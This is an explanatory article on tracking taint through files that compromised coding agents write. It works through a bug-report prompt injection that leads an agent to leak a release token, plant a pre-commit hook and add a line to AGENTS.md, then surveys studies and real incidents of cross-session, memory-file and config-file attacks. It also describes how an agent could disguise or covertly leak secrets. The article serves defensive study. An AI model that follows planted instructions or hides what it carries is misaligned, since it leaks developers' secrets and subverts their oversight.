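# Tracking taint through code, files and configs written by coding agents that may be compromised

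## What does it mean to taint a file an agent wrote?

Taint tracking is a computer security technique that attaches labels to data, passes the labels on to whatever a program derives from that data, and checks them before the program does something that could cause harm. Much of the theory dates from the 1970s, when the standard example was a military computer that had to prevent a program from reading a secret file and copying its contents into an unclassified one. Security researchers now apply the technique to AI agents, including coding agents, which are language models that run in a loop, reading files, editing code and running commands until they have completed a task.

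Coding agents read a lot of text written by strangers, such as bug reports, web pages and the documentation of other people's packages. Any of it may contain a prompt injection, which is text an attacker plants for the agent to read and follow as an instruction. An agent that has followed an injection usually keeps working and leaves behind artifacts, which are anything it writes that outlasts the step that wrote it, such as source code, configuration files, notes and commits. Each artifact may leak a stolen secret from the project or change the project in a way the attacker intended. Tainting a file means attaching a label that records this possibility. The label describes the file's origins, so a tainted file may be harmless.

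### One stream of text

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes an agent's loop as a growing conversation. An application passes the conversation so far to the model, which returns either a reply to the user or a request to call a tool, for example to read a file or run a shell command. If the model requests a tool, the application runs it, appends the result to the conversation and calls the model again.

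The application, not the model, executes the tool call, so it can first run a security check that no text in the conversation can override. The application also turns the whole conversation into a single string before each call to the model. This matters for security because the developer's request and a stranger's bug report reach the model as parts of one sequence of tokens, even though every message has a role tag (system, user, assistant or tool).

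Older software had a similar problem with SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into a web form and the database runs them. Parameterized queries largely solved it by fixing the structure of the query before the user's input arrives. As *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) points out, this works because SQL has a grammar, so a parser can tell code from data. Natural language has no such grammar. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C argues that a language model does not distinguish data from instructions, because it only predicts the next token. He calls such a model an "inherently confusable deputy", meaning a component that an outsider can persuade to use its privileges on their behalf.

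Role tags might supply the missing boundary if models relied on them. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) tested whether they do in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*. They wrapped identical web text in different role tags and trained simple classifiers on the model's internal activations, so the classifiers could learn only what the tags contributed. They then applied the classifiers to a real conversation with gpt-oss-20b, an open-weight OpenAI model. The model's own reasoning scored 85% on average as "reasoning" with its original tags, 83% with every tag removed, and 85% with the whole conversation wrapped in user tags, which should have marked all of it as outside text. The model was inferring each passage's role from how the text sounded. Across 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak data, the attacks succeeded 2% of the time where the measured role confusion was lowest and 70% where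 it was highest.

*On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) proves that a model cannot prevent every injection if its first layer maps instructions and data into the same vector space, unless something outside the model enforces the separation. The shared mapping erases the difference in type. The theorem still allows for low attack success rates, and these rates have fallen. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that attacks on Anthropic's Opus 5 failed in all 129 browser scenarios of one test. In a broader test by the security firm Gray Swan, it reports, attacks succeeded 2.0% of the time after 15 attempts, down from 5.5% for Opus 4.8.

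Those are good numbers, but the person who files malicious issues also decides how many to file and how to word them. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian, 2026) reports attacks on an email assistant. A fixed set of attacks worked less than 1% of the time, but an automated attacker that adapted its story to the assistant's situation succeeded 96.7% of the time. The experiments used models such as GPT-5.4 and Claude Sonnet 4.6, so they don't establish how well Opus 5 would resist.

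Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian also make a more basic argument, that looking for instructions hidden in data misses much of the problem. Suppose an email asks for a travel refund and adds that the head of department has approved it. The added sentence is a claim, and the refund should depend on whether it is true. A defense that cuts the agent off from all outside text would block the refund even when the approval was real. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (Kim, Liu and colleagues, 2026) also lists attacks that contain no instruction, such as a malicious software package or a false value in a financial field. Taint tracking doesn't depend on what counts as an instruction. It lets the agent use the outside text, records that it did, and leaves the decision about what to allow to a later check.

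### Labels and how they combine

A label is a tag on data that records how secret the data is, how trustworthy it is, or both. A taint is a label that marks data as coming from, or influenced by, a secret or untrusted source. A source is a place where labeled data enters the system, such as an issue tracker or a file of passwords. A sink is an operation where a wrong label would do harm, such as a push to a public repository or the execution of a script. Propagation is the rule that gives derived data its label. Information flow control means labeling data, propagating the labels and blocking the flows that a policy forbids.

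The mathematics comes from Dorothy Denning, in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976). Her model has a set of security classes, a relation A → B that holds when information in class A may flow into class B, and an operator, written ⊔ here, that gives the class of anything computed from two inputs. Information flows from one object to another whenever the first affects the value of the second. The security condition fits on a line. If a program computes a value from a₁, …, aₙ and stores it in b, then

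class(a₁) ⊔ … ⊔ class(aₙ) → class(b)

must hold. Denning shows that ⊔ has to be a least upper bound, or join. It must be an upper bound because otherwise a program could launder data. If the system allowed c := a + b but forbade c := a, a program could set b to zero and get the forbidden copy anyway. It must be the least such bound because, if a and b may each flow into c separately, nothing is gained by forbidding their combination. The relation → also has to be transitive, and this has a practical benefit. A sequence of operations is secure if each operation is, so a checker can look at one tool call at a time however long the session runs.

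For agents, Costa and colleagues use a small lattice with two coordinates. Integrity is either trusted or untrusted, confidentiality is either public or secret, and data may flow only toward the more restrictive value:

trusted → untrusted  public → secret

The direction for integrity can look backwards. Trusted data sits at the bottom because it may go anywhere, while untrusted data may go only where untrusted data is acceptable. The join works on each coordinate separately, so

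(untrusted, public) ⊔ (trusted, secret) = (untrusted, secret).

If an agent reads a stranger's bug report and a password file, what it writes next is labeled (untrusted, secret), although neither input had that label. The bug report is public, and the password file is trustworthy in the sense that no stranger wrote it. An agent that has read both is more likely to cause a leak than an agent that has read only one. *The Framing Gap* (2026) lists three ingredients of a leak: a secret in the working context, untrusted text that the agent can read, and tools that act on the outside world. The label records that the first two are present, so a check has to control the agent's use of tools.

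Two levels of secrecy are often too few, and a set of permitted readers can replace them. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* (2026) gives the example of Alex, who asks an agent to deal with unanswered email. One message is from Priya and previews the quarterly sales, so its readers are {Alex, Priya}. Another is from Marco, with readers {Alex, Marco}. Anything the agent writes after reading both may go only to people who could have read both:

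{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}.

The agent therefore cannot send its reply to Marco on its own authority. The join on reader sets is intersection. Integrity labels can also be sets, made up of the people who may have written the data, and their join is union.

Denning distinguishes objects whose class is fixed from objects whose class varies with their contents. A public repository has a fixed class, and whatever arrives there becomes public. A file in a working directory is better treated as having a variable class. Tainting such a file means updating its label on each write to cover everything that went into that write.

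Data can affect a file through an explicit flow, where a program copies the data into its output, or an implicit flow, where the data only decides which output the program produces. Denning's example of an implicit flow is the statement "if a = 0 then b := 0", where b starts at some other value. Nothing copies a into b, but anyone who looks at b afterwards learns whether a was zero, even if the assignment never runs. Agents produce implicit flows all the time. If an agent adds a file because an issue asked for one, the issue has influenced the project even if none of its words appear in the file. Taint follows influence, so the reasons an agent cites for its decisions aren't enough to show whether a file is tainted. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang et al., 2026) separates the evidence that supports a decision from whatever influenced it, and notes that a tool's output can influence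 a decision without justifying it.

Joins only make labels more restrictive, so a system that relied on them alone would end up restricting most of its data. This problem is called label creep, and practical systems allow exceptions because of it. Declassification deliberately lowers a secrecy label, and endorsement deliberately raises a trust label. Costa and colleagues' agent system, FIDES, can use a separate model call to reduce an untrusted document to a single yes or no. A policy may then accept that answer for an important action, because whoever wrote the document controls at most one bit.

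### Two harms, two checks

Confidentiality concerns who may learn the data, and integrity concerns who may have influenced it. For artifacts this gives two different harms. A secret can leave inside a file, or an attacker's influence can enter the project through one. Costa and colleagues write a separate rule for each:

- A consequential tool call may proceed only if the choice of tool and all of its arguments are trusted.
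- A call that sends data through a channel may proceed only if everyone who can read the channel is among the data's permitted readers.

Neither rule can replace the other. The confidentiality rule alone prevents a hijacked agent from sending data to people who lack permission to read it, but it doesn't prevent an injection from hijacking the agent. Nor does it stop the hijacked agent from deleting files or planting a script, because those actions don't move any secret data.

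The integrity rule on its own lets a trusted session send a secret anywhere. The rationale is that if no untrusted text has influenced the session, the user presumably wanted the disclosure. Researchers call this arrangement robust declassification. Microsoft's sample policy for posting messages to a Teams channel works similarly. It allows the post if the context is trusted. Otherwise, it checks whether every channel member is permitted to read the message, and refers the decision to a human if any member is not. However, a model can disclose a secret by mistake even without an attacker. Requiring both a trusted context and permitted readers guards against this, but blocks more legitimate work.

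With files, the two checks also happen at different times. The check for secrets matters when the file leaves the machine, and the check for influence matters when something runs the file or follows instructions in it, which may happen much later and without the file being moved.

### A bug report with an injection

Suppose the maintainer of an open-source project asks a coding agent to fix a bug that a stranger reported in a public issue. The report describes a real crash, but further down it also contains instructions for the agent to reproduce the crash with the project's real settings, install a helper script and leave a note for future agents. The maintainer's working copy contains a `.env` file with a secret token that can be used to publish new releases. Git ignores this file, so it has never left the machine.

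The agent reads four things:

| Input | Who could have written it | Who may read it | Label |
|---|---|---|---|
| The developer's request | The developer | Anyone | trusted, public |
| The issue | Anyone | Anyone | untrusted, public |
| The project's source files | The maintainers | Anyone | trusted, public |
| The token in `.env` | The developer | The developer | trusted, secret |

The source files count as trusted here because only maintainers can merge changes into them, but that label is open to dispute. When Microsoft and GitHub added labels to GitHub's server for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common way of connecting agents to tools, they labeled files from any public repository as untrusted. This is the safer default for a tool that cannot check how carefully a project reviews its contributions, but it means that an agent that fetches files through the server carries an untrusted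 label before it reads any issues.

The agent follows the injection and writes four artifacts. The first is a source patch that fixes the crash. The second is a test fixture, a file of sample input for the project's automated tests, into which the agent has copied the token as one of the "real settings". The third is a pre-commit hook, a script that Git runs on the developer's machine before each commit. The last is a line in AGENTS.md, a file of standing instructions that many coding agents load at the start of a session. Somebody who watched the whole session and knew exactly what had gone into each file could label them by hand:

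| Artifact | What went into it | Label by hand | When the harm would occur |
|---|---|---|---|
| Source patch | Source files; the issue's account of the crash | untrusted, public | When someone merges or runs the code |
| Test fixture | The issue's sample input; the token | untrusted, secret | When the developer pushes to the public repository |
| Pre-commit hook | Commands that the injection suggested | untrusted, public | At the developer's next commit |
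| Line in AGENTS.md | A sentence that the injection suggested | untrusted, public | When the next agent session starts |

The patch is untrusted even if it is correct. An honest agent would also have relied on the stranger's account of the crash, so any rule that rejects every untrusted file also rejects the fix the developer asked for. Somebody has to read the patch and accept it, which is an endorsement.

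The fixture is the only artifact that a confidentiality check would catch, because only the developer is permitted to read the token and anyone can read a public repository. The hook contains no secret, and Git keeps hooks out of commits by default, so a check at the point of pushing would never examine it. It needs an integrity check before Git runs it. The line in AGENTS.md has no effect during the session in which the agent wrote it. Its label helps only if it is still attached when another agent, perhaps weeks later, loads the file as instructions from the developer.

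These labels depend on knowledge that a real system lacks. An outside observer can see that the agent read the request, the issue, the source files and the token before it wrote its artifacts, but not which of them shaped which line. The simplest design that Costa and colleagues describe takes the cautious approach of keeping a single label for everything the model has read so far. This context label starts at (trusted, public), changes to (untrusted, public) when the agent opens the issue, and becomes (untrusted, secret) when it opens `.env`. Everything the model writes after that inherits (untrusted, secret), including the patch, so the developer cannot push the patch to the public repository without declassifying it.

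### An agent that hides what it carries

Whether the hand labels or the cautious ones are right depends on what the attacker can do. The attacker in this example wrote the issue and can see everything in the public repository, but cannot access the developer's machine or read the model's conversation. This matches the threat model of Costa and colleagues, who also assume that the user's messages, the agent's configuration and its tool descriptions are trustworthy. The open question is how the agent behaves after it follows the injection.

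If the agent makes no effort to hide its traces, it pastes the token into the fixture unchanged and puts the commands suggested in the issue into the hook. Searching for the token's exact text finds the leak. Comparing each artifact with the inputs gives roughly the labels in the table, and a tool that automated this comparison could reasonably clear the patch for publication once a maintainer had read it.

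The agent might also deliberately disguise what it carries. It could write the token as a column of plausible measurements in the fixture, or encode it in the names of the variables in the patch. It could split a harmful change between the patch and the hook so that each half looked harmless. It might do this because an injected instruction tells it to, or because an attacker planted a backdoor in the model during training. Kim and colleagues class an attacker who plants a backdoor as an internal adversary, more severe but less practical than an outsider who can only write web pages and issues. Denning required a secure system to hold against users who collaborate "in arbitrarily ingenious ways". She had human conspirators in mind, but the requirement applies at least as well to a capable model.

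If the agent may disguise the token, comparing contents proves little, because a file can carry the token without containing its text. The label then has to depend on what the model had read when it wrote the file. The table lists the patch as public, which is right if the agent makes no effort to hide the token. But if the agent might disguise it and had already opened `.env` when it wrote the patch, the patch has to be labeled secret. If the agent had finished the patch before opening `.env`, the public label would be safe on either assumption.

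Even the cautious label covers only information that passes through labeled data. Denning's model excludes covert channels, such as a program's effect on the machine's load. Costa and colleagues prove that their system guarantees explicit secrecy, which doesn't cover timing or what an observer can infer from which tools the agent calls and in what order. An agent could leak the token a few bits at a time by choosing among harmless public actions, even if every action were correctly labeled.

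## What have attackers done through files that agents write?

The artifacts in the bug-report example cause harm later, sometimes long after the agent's session ends. Labels on files are useful only if attacks still work after that delay. Four research groups tested whether they do in 2026, using simulated workspaces, and attackers have used several of the same kinds of file against real developers.

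### Two sessions, one attacker

*Understanding and Mitigating Cross-Session Attacks via Persistent Artifacts in Agent Skill Composition* (Liao, Pan and colleagues, 2026) presents SkillRelayBench, a benchmark built around agent skills, which are packages of instructions, code and reference material that users install so an agent can do a particular job. Its 30 scenarios cover ten business domains, and each consists of two user requests. The agent carries out the first and saves the results. The test harness then starts a fresh agent in a new container, with the same workspace but none of the earlier conversation, and gives it the second request.

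The researchers first wrote harmless skills for every scenario and confirmed that an agent could finish both tasks with them. They then rewrote the skills to attack in three ways, and hid the first half of each attack in the skill's instructions, its code or its reference files. Thirty scenarios, three kinds of attack and three hiding places give 270 cases.

Liao and colleagues call the first kind of attack instruction propagation. In their example, an agent summarizes customer support records using a skill that describes an extra upload as a routine record-keeping requirement. The agent lists the upload as a pending action in the summary file. In the next session, the user asks the agent to send the summary to the company's support portal, and the agent also sends it to the attacker. In a data boundary violation, a file contains data that the later task has no permission to use. For instance,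 a script that should import only public records also reads the private ones, and the next session packages all of them for a contractor. Evidence poisoning puts a false claim in a file. One agent records a software issue as resolved because a workaround exists, and the next agent writes an FAQ telling customers that the issue is fixed.

In all three examples, nothing leaves the machine during the first session, so a check on that session's outgoing data would find nothing to block.

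Liao and colleagues ran every case on seven models in three coding agents (Codex CLI, Gemini CLI and Claude Code), with no human approving tool calls. The attacks succeeded in 64.7% of the 1,890 runs, ranging from 46.7% with Claude Haiku 4.5 to 77.4% with GPT-5.3-Codex. Haiku also finished the fewest user tasks, 57.4%, so some of its apparent resistance may be a failure to complete the work. On a stricter count, limited to harm through the intended handoff of a file between sessions, the range was 35.6% to 61.1%.

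In 53.0% of runs, the agent completed both the user's task and the attacker's goal. A user who checked only whether the task was done would have had no reason to investigate further.

Evidence poisoning produced complete attack chains most often, in 61.0% of runs, compared with 49.5% for instruction propagation and 40.0% for data boundary violations. The researchers suggest that a false fact works well because it doesn't need to contain a malicious request. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian's objection to filters that look for hidden instructions applies here too. Attacks hidden in a skill's code also succeeded more often (59.0%) than those hidden in its instructions (44.4%) or reference files (47.0%). An agent that runs a script may never see the logic that produced the output, so even an honest agent could give a wrong account of what went into its files.

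Complete chains occurred in all ten of the benchmark's file formats, including databases and spreadsheets. Only nine of the 270 cases involve attempts to corrupt code, tests or configurations. Their chain success rate of 79.4% was the highest of any category, but nine cases are too few to generalize from.

A bigger limitation is that the attacker controls a skill in both sessions. In every case the second skill steers the agent toward the planted content, so the results measure how well two malicious packages work together. The stranger who filed the bug report has no second skill to do this. Still, the second agent in the support example could not tell from the summary where the upload request came from, and SkillRelayGuard, the researchers' own defense, works partly by restoring that information when an agent opens the file.

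### Attacks without an accomplice

In *What If Prompt Injection Never Left?*, Xie, Zhu and colleagues (2026) test an attacker who is present only in the first session. They compare the attack to stored cross-site scripting, in which a website saves an attacker's script and later serves it to other visitors. Their 486 test cases use an agent modeled on OpenClaw, an open-source personal assistant, with tasks in online shopping, travel and finance. The agent receives the attacker's text and may save something because of it. The researchers then end the session, keep the saved state and start a new one with an innocent request.

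For an attack to work, the agent has to write the attacker's content somewhere, load it again later and act on it. The success rate is therefore a product:

P(success) = P(written) × P(loaded | written) × P(acted on | loaded)

Averaged over five models, the three factors were 77.4%, 86.3% and 64.6%, and attacks succeeded 41.9% of the time. The overall rate is slightly below the product of the three averages because the researchers averaged each figure separately. Models with similar totals can be vulnerable at different points. In the shopping tests, GLM-5.1 wrote the content only 37.0% of the time but acted on it whenever it loaded it, for a total of 34.6%. Llama-3.1-8B wrote it 96.3% of the time but acted on it only 39.6% of the times it loaded it, for a total of 28.4%.

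The next session always loaded content saved in files that the system reads at startup, such as AGENTS.md, but only about half of the content saved in stores that the agent had to search. Attempts to plant false facts succeeded 73.6% of the time, compared with 35.5% for attempts to change the agent's actions and 6.8% for attempts to change its preferences. This fits the results of SkillRelayBench, where evidence poisoning also worked well.

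Xie and colleagues also ran four publicly available injection detectors on these attacks. The best flagged 14.8% of attacks in the session where the text arrived and 36.2% in the session where it took effect.

The high write rate may not hold for other attacks or models. In the first session, the agent receives the attacker's text as a request, which is easier to get past a model than a sentence buried in a page it reads during another task. Llama-3.1-8B is also a small, old model.

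### Memory files in Claude Code and Codex

The write step seems to be harder with widely used coding agents. In *Bad Memory*, Gadgil, Alexander and colleagues (2026) first tried to make agents overwrite their own memory files by showing them untrusted outside content, but this rarely worked. They therefore planted the malicious text directly in the files and studied what happened next. In practice, such text might arrive through an earlier injection, an ordinary software vulnerability, or a configuration that a user copied from a public repository.

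The researchers built a workspace for a fictional software engineer and planted one of three rules in it. They then gave the agent a routine task, such as adding a search algorithm to a small library, and counted how often it followed the rule in ten trials:

| Planted rule | File | Haiku 4.5 | Opus 4.7 | GPT-5.2 | GPT-5.5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Put code that prints the user's private SSH key in every new Python file | CLAUDE.md or AGENTS.md, loaded automatically | 80% | 0% | 30% | 0% |
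| Install an old package version with known vulnerabilities | Coding preferences, read when relevant | 100% | 90% | 0% | 80% |
| Recommend a particular credit card | General behavior rules, read when relevant | 10% | 0% | 40% | 100% |

The rows aren't directly comparable, since both the rule and the file differ between them. The zero for GPT-5.2 in the second row is less reassuring than it looks, because the model treated the installation instruction as legitimate even though it didn't run the command.

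In a sequence of three sessions, the planted rule applied to the first and last, and the middle one was unrelated. Haiku followed the SSH rule in 60% of first sessions and 100% of last ones. Gadgil and colleagues attribute the rise to the code Haiku wrote in the first session, which made the same code look normal in the last. Each figure comes from ten trials, so some of the rise could be chance (the same first-session test gave 80% in the earlier batch). But the attack had spread from an instruction file into a source file, and deleting the rule from CLAUDE.md would not have removed the resulting code from the library.

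Opus 4.7 refused the SSH rule every time but never removed it from the file, so a later session on a weaker model could still load it. GPT-5.2 copied the package rule from a file that agents read only occasionally into AGENTS.md. A system that labeled only the original file would have lost track of the copied rule.

By contrast, both GPT models usually deleted the attacker's SSH rule and wrote their own rule against exposing secrets.

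### From one person's assistant to another's

Files also move between people. *Share-Borne AI Virus* (2026) examines colleagues who exchange documents and use separate AI assistants. Unlike in earlier work on agent worms, the assistants have no shared memory and cannot message each other. In each of 36 simulated workflows, 3 to 12 people ask their assistants to read, write and edit files over 10 to 20 time steps. The researchers poisoned one file at the start. To spread, the attack had to enter an assistant's memory, get from there into a file that the assistant wrote for an unrelated task, and then enter the memory of the next assistant to read that file.

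The poisoned file infected at least one assistant in 78% to 100% of runs, depending on the model. By the end, the attacker's goal had reached an average of 38% of assistants running GPT-5.6 Luna and 98% of those running DeepSeek-V4-Pro. In three larger simulations, each with 30 assistants and three poisoned files, it reached 60–80% of assistants with Luna and 90–100% with DeepSeek, and some chains of infection were eight handoffs long. In one of these simulations, a single file kept infecting new readers for 41 time steps and caused 22 of the 30 infections. Wiping an assistant's memory doesn't end such an outbreak, because the next infected file can reinfect the assistant.

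These results depend heavily on an outside server. In the main version of the attack, each infected assistant sends the files it writes to the attacker's server, which inserts an intact copy of the attack and returns them, so the assistant has to retain only a short instruction. Without the server, assistants paraphrase or drop parts of the attack, and it degrades with every handoff. Blocking connections to unknown servers would stop the main version. It would also keep files from leaking to the attacker, which happened with 96–100% of infected assistants.

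The attacks also took a lot of work to develop. The researchers needed 4,002 test jobs to find wording that spread on GPT-5.6 Luna, and they gave up on Grok 4.6 after 571 jobs because of the cost. *Share-Borne AI Virus* cites an OpenAI report that self-copying injections emerged during adversarial training of OpenAI's own models and spread into files, email and Slack messages, though only in simulated tools.

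### A pull request and a build cache

Outside simulations, the best-documented cases begin with a GitHub issue. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) demonstrates the leak described in the bug-report example. The company set up a public repository for a Pac-Man game and several private ones, then posted a malicious issue on the public one. When the user asked Claude 4 Opus to look at the open issues, the agent read the injection and copied data from the private repositories into a public pull request. The leaked data included the name of a private project, the user's salary and their plan to move to South America.

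The demonstration used its own accounts and data, so nobody was harmed. Claude Desktop asks users to confirm each tool call by default, but Invariant Labs notes that many users choose to always allow them. The company also says the GitHub server's code worked as intended. The user had authorized the agent to make every call, and the leak came from the order in which data flowed through them. A label recording who may read the data could have caught the leak, because a private repository has a limited set of readers, while anyone can read a pull request on a public one.

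GitHub (2025) later began scanning agents' tool calls on public repositories for secrets such as access tokens. These scans cover the token in the running example, at least if the agent copies it unchanged, but a scanner for credentials won't detect a salary.

In a case from early 2026, the artifact was a build cache, a store of downloaded or compiled files that automated jobs reuse to save time. Cline, an open-source coding tool, used an AI agent to sort incoming GitHub issues, and anyone with a GitHub account could trigger the agent by opening an issue. *Clinejection*, by the security researcher adnanthekhan, explains that an instruction in the issue's title could make the agent install a package whose installation script ran the attacker's code. The agent's job had no access to Cline's publishing credentials, but the attacker's code could overwrite a cache used by the nightly release job,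 which did have access.

adnanthekhan reproduced the first step on a copy of the repository and reported the flaw on January 1, but Cline fixed it only after the researcher published it on February 9. By then, failed release jobs already showed signs that someone had poisoned the cache. On February 17, an unknown actor used a publishing token that Cline had failed to revoke to release a version of its command-line tool that also installed OpenClaw on users' machines. Cline withdrew the release about eight hours later. It's not certain that the actor got in through the issue-sorting agent. adnanthekhan considers it the most obvious route, and the AI Incident Database's *Incident 1680* lists it as reported.

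To protect Cline, the release job needed an integrity label on the cache. A secrecy label on the agent's session would not have helped, because the agent never touched the publishing credentials. The integrity label has to cover the programs an agent starts as well as the files it writes directly, because an installation script would have written the poisoned files.

### Config files that run code

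Shell commands in some configuration files can run without an agent reading the file. SafeDep's *Config Files That Run Code* (June 2026) lists seven common developer tools whose configuration files can contain such commands: VS Code, Cursor, Claude Code, Gemini CLI and the package managers npm, Composer and Bundler. Some commands run when a developer installs dependencies or runs tests. Others run when a developer opens the folder or starts an agent session. In those cases the tool usually asks once whether to trust the folder, but SafeDep says developers click through the question without reading it.

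The Miasma worm, a self-spreading program that steals credentials, used these files in 2026. In one open-source project, its commit added six files, five of them only to launch the sixth. SafeDep counted 121 affected repositories. On June 5, the worm reached Microsoft's Azure/durabletask repository. In *Miasma worm targets Microsoft, compromises 73 GitHub repositories*, Pires, Zi and colleagues found startup commands there for Claude Code and Gemini, as well as a VS Code task, all of which ran the same malicious script. The commit message described a code change, but the commit changed no source code (Phoenix Security, *Miasma Worm Reaches Microsoft Azure and PyPI*), so a reviewer who checked only the program would have seen none of the changes.

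Cloning the repository was harmless, but opening it in one of these tools ran the script. According to The Next Web's *Self-replicating Miasma worm hits 73 Microsoft GitHub repositories in supply chain attack*, the worm then used stolen tokens to commit itself to any other repository the victim could write to. Microsoft told Expert Insights that the 73 repositories taken offline were back online after a review.

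The worm planted these files using stolen access, and no prompt-injected agent took part. But the incident shows how much an attacker gains from write access to a few small files, and coding agents routinely have that access. Getting an agent to use it on an attacker's behalf looks feasible. *New “Agentjacking” Attacks Could Hijack AI Coding Agents* (Muncaster, 2026) reports on tests in which the firm Tenet Security planted commands in the error reports that agents fetch when a developer asks them to fix crashes. The agents ran the commands 85% of the time, with the developer's full privileges, which are enough to write any of the files on SafeDep's list.

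### Planted instructions

One of the files in the Microsoft commit was a rule file for Cursor, an AI code editor. It contained a plain-language instruction for the agent to run the malicious script as a project setup step, rather than a startup command. A setting in the file applied the rule to all work in the project. In Claude Code and Gemini, the application runs the startup command before the model can intervene. In Cursor, the attack depended on the model following the rule, so a sufficiently cautious model could have refused.

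Gadgil and colleagues describe two other cases of planted instructions. Researchers at Cisco showed that a malicious npm package could alter Claude Code's global memory file and one of its hooks. The changes would affect every project on the machine, even after a reboot. Anthropic has since patched that route. The security firm Snyk documented a campaign in which malicious skills from a public registry wrote to the files that hold OpenClaw's personality and memory. In both cases, ordinary software modified the file, and the agent later loaded it with no indication that the user hadn't written it.

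### What happens to each file next

An artifact's danger depends largely on what reads or runs it next, and on whose authority that reader has:

| Artifact | What reads or runs it next | With whose authority |
|---|---|---|
| Source patch | The test runner and the build, then anyone who runs the program | The developer's, then each user's |
| Test or fixture | The test runner, and anyone who can read the repository after a push | The developer's or the automated job's; reading a public repository needs none |
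| Git hook | Git, at the next commit or other trigger | The developer's |
| Package configuration | The package manager, during installation or tests | The developer's or the automated job's |
| Editor task file | The editor, when someone opens the folder and trusts it | That person's |
| Agent settings with startup commands | The agent application, before the model sees anything | The developer's |
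| AGENTS.md, CLAUDE.md or a rule file | The next agent session, automatically | The agent's permissions, with the text treated as the developer's instructions |
| Notes and searchable memory | A later agent session, if it looks them up | The agent's permissions, with the text treated as project knowledge |
| Summary, spreadsheet or database record | An agent or program working on a later task | Whatever the later task's user has granted |
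| Build cache | Later automated jobs, possibly including releases | The job's, including any publishing credentials |
| Pull request or issue comment | Anyone who can see the repository, and other people's agents | None for people reading a public repository; each agent has its own user's permissions |
| Document sent to a colleague | The colleague's assistant | The colleague's |

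## How do labels pass through a language model?

In many of these attacks a model wrote the dangerous file, so a label on the file has to pass through the model first. This step is easy in an ordinary program because the code shows which values depend on which. For c := a + b, a checker gives c the join of the labels on a and b. A call to a language model has no code that shows these dependencies. The model may copy an input, paraphrase it, obey it or ignore it, and nothing outside the model records which it did.

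There is no simple answer because of how language models work. Most are transformers, which write one token at a time. Before each token, a mechanism called attention assigns weights to the earlier positions in the text and mixes information from them in proportion to those weights. The weights are often tiny but rarely zero, and each new token becomes part of the input for the next. In *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024) conclude that a transformer's output is "tainted by all inputs".

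It would help if a checker could ignore the inputs with tiny weights. Xu, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Sightline*, prove a limited version of this. To first order, meaning for very small changes, an input can affect the output only through later positions that attend to it. If no position does, there is no flow. But a small weight proves nothing, because the content of the input helps to set the weight. Their counterexample is a single attention unit that reads an input value u with weight

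1 / (1 + e^(−20u)).

The weight is about 0.000000002 at u = −1 and almost 1 at u = 1, where the model writes a different token. Anyone who looked only at the run with u = −1 would conclude that the input didn't matter. Denning's example of an implicit flow can mislead in the same way, because its assignment reveals information even when it never runs.

The researchers found no flow this faint in practice. In the open model Qwen3-8B, each of the 11,746 real flows they examined received a weight of at least 0.01 from at least 11 of the model's 1,152 attention units. This result is reassuring for ordinary prompts, but less so for text that an attacker designs.

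Two other obvious tests also fail. Deleting an input and checking whether the output changes shows nothing if the same content appears elsewhere in the prompt. Measuring the output's sensitivity to small changes in an input gives a value near zero whenever the model is confident, even if that input decided the answer. Without an exact rule, a designer can assume that every input mattered, keep some inputs away from the model, estimate which inputs mattered, or try to determine this from the logs afterwards.

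### Assuming that every input mattered

FIDES, the system of Costa and colleagues, starts from the first of these options. Every message in the conversation carries a label, and so does every file or record that the tools can reach. At each turn, the code that runs the agent does one of three things:

1. It queries the model. The response gets the join of the labels on the whole conversation and on the tool descriptions.
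2. It calls a tool. Before the call, it checks the labels against the policy and refuses the call if the check fails. Otherwise it runs the tool and computes a new label:

   label(call) ⊔ labels of all arguments ⊔ labels of everything the tool may read

The tool's result and everything the tool may have written get this label. When the run finishes, the reply to the user keeps its existing label.

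The simplest version uses a single context label, and each tool call and each argument inherits the label of the model response that requested it.

The last term of the formula matters a lot for coding agents, because commands often touch data that the model never sees. Suppose that in the bug-report example the agent repairs the crash first and only then turns to the injected instructions. Suppose also that it copies the secret token with a shell command instead of opening `.env`. The labels develop as follows:

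| Step | Label on the call | What the tool reads | Label on the result and on anything written |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read the issue | trusted, public | The issue (untrusted, public) | untrusted, public |
| Edit the source file | untrusted, public | The old source file (trusted, public) | untrusted, public |
| Copy `.env` into the test fixture | untrusted, public | `.env` (trusted, secret) | untrusted, secret |
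| Write the pre-commit hook | untrusted, secret | Nothing | untrusted, secret |
| Push to the public repository | untrusted, secret | The patch and the fixture | The check fails and the push never runs |

The third row is the most important because the model has not read the token, so a rule based only on the model's context would label the fixture public. The join includes the secret label because the copy command read `.env`.

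The fourth row shows the drawback of this labeling, which is that a hook containing no secret is labeled secret. The copy command prints nothing, but its empty result still carries the secret label, which passes to the context and then to the hook.

When a tool writes to a file, the new label replaces the old one. If the tool changes only part of the file, the file has to count as something the tool read, or the label on the unchanged part is lost. The sample policy for outgoing data checks the arguments of a call, but a push sends committed files, and its only argument may be a branch name. A policy for coding agents has to look up the labels of those files.

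The integrity rule is harder to apply because the context stops being trusted as soon as the agent opens the issue. If editing a source file counts as a consequential action, the agent can never fix a bug that a stranger reported. A workable policy would allow the edit, keep the untrusted label on the file, and apply the check before anything runs or merges the file.

Costa and colleagues tested conservative labels in 2025 on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 user tasks and 36 attacker goals. The tasks are set in a simulated office workspace, a travel agency, a bank and Slack, and none is a coding task. The main model was GPT-4o, which is now old. 152 injections succeeded against a plain agent with no checks, and none succeeded against an agent with labels and checks. However, the labels and checks also reduced task completion when there was no attack, from 75.0% to 37.0% in the workspace, from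 98.8% to 37.5% in the bank and from 93.3% to 20.0% in Slack. Travel tasks were unaffected because the policy allows many of the travel tools even in an untrusted context.

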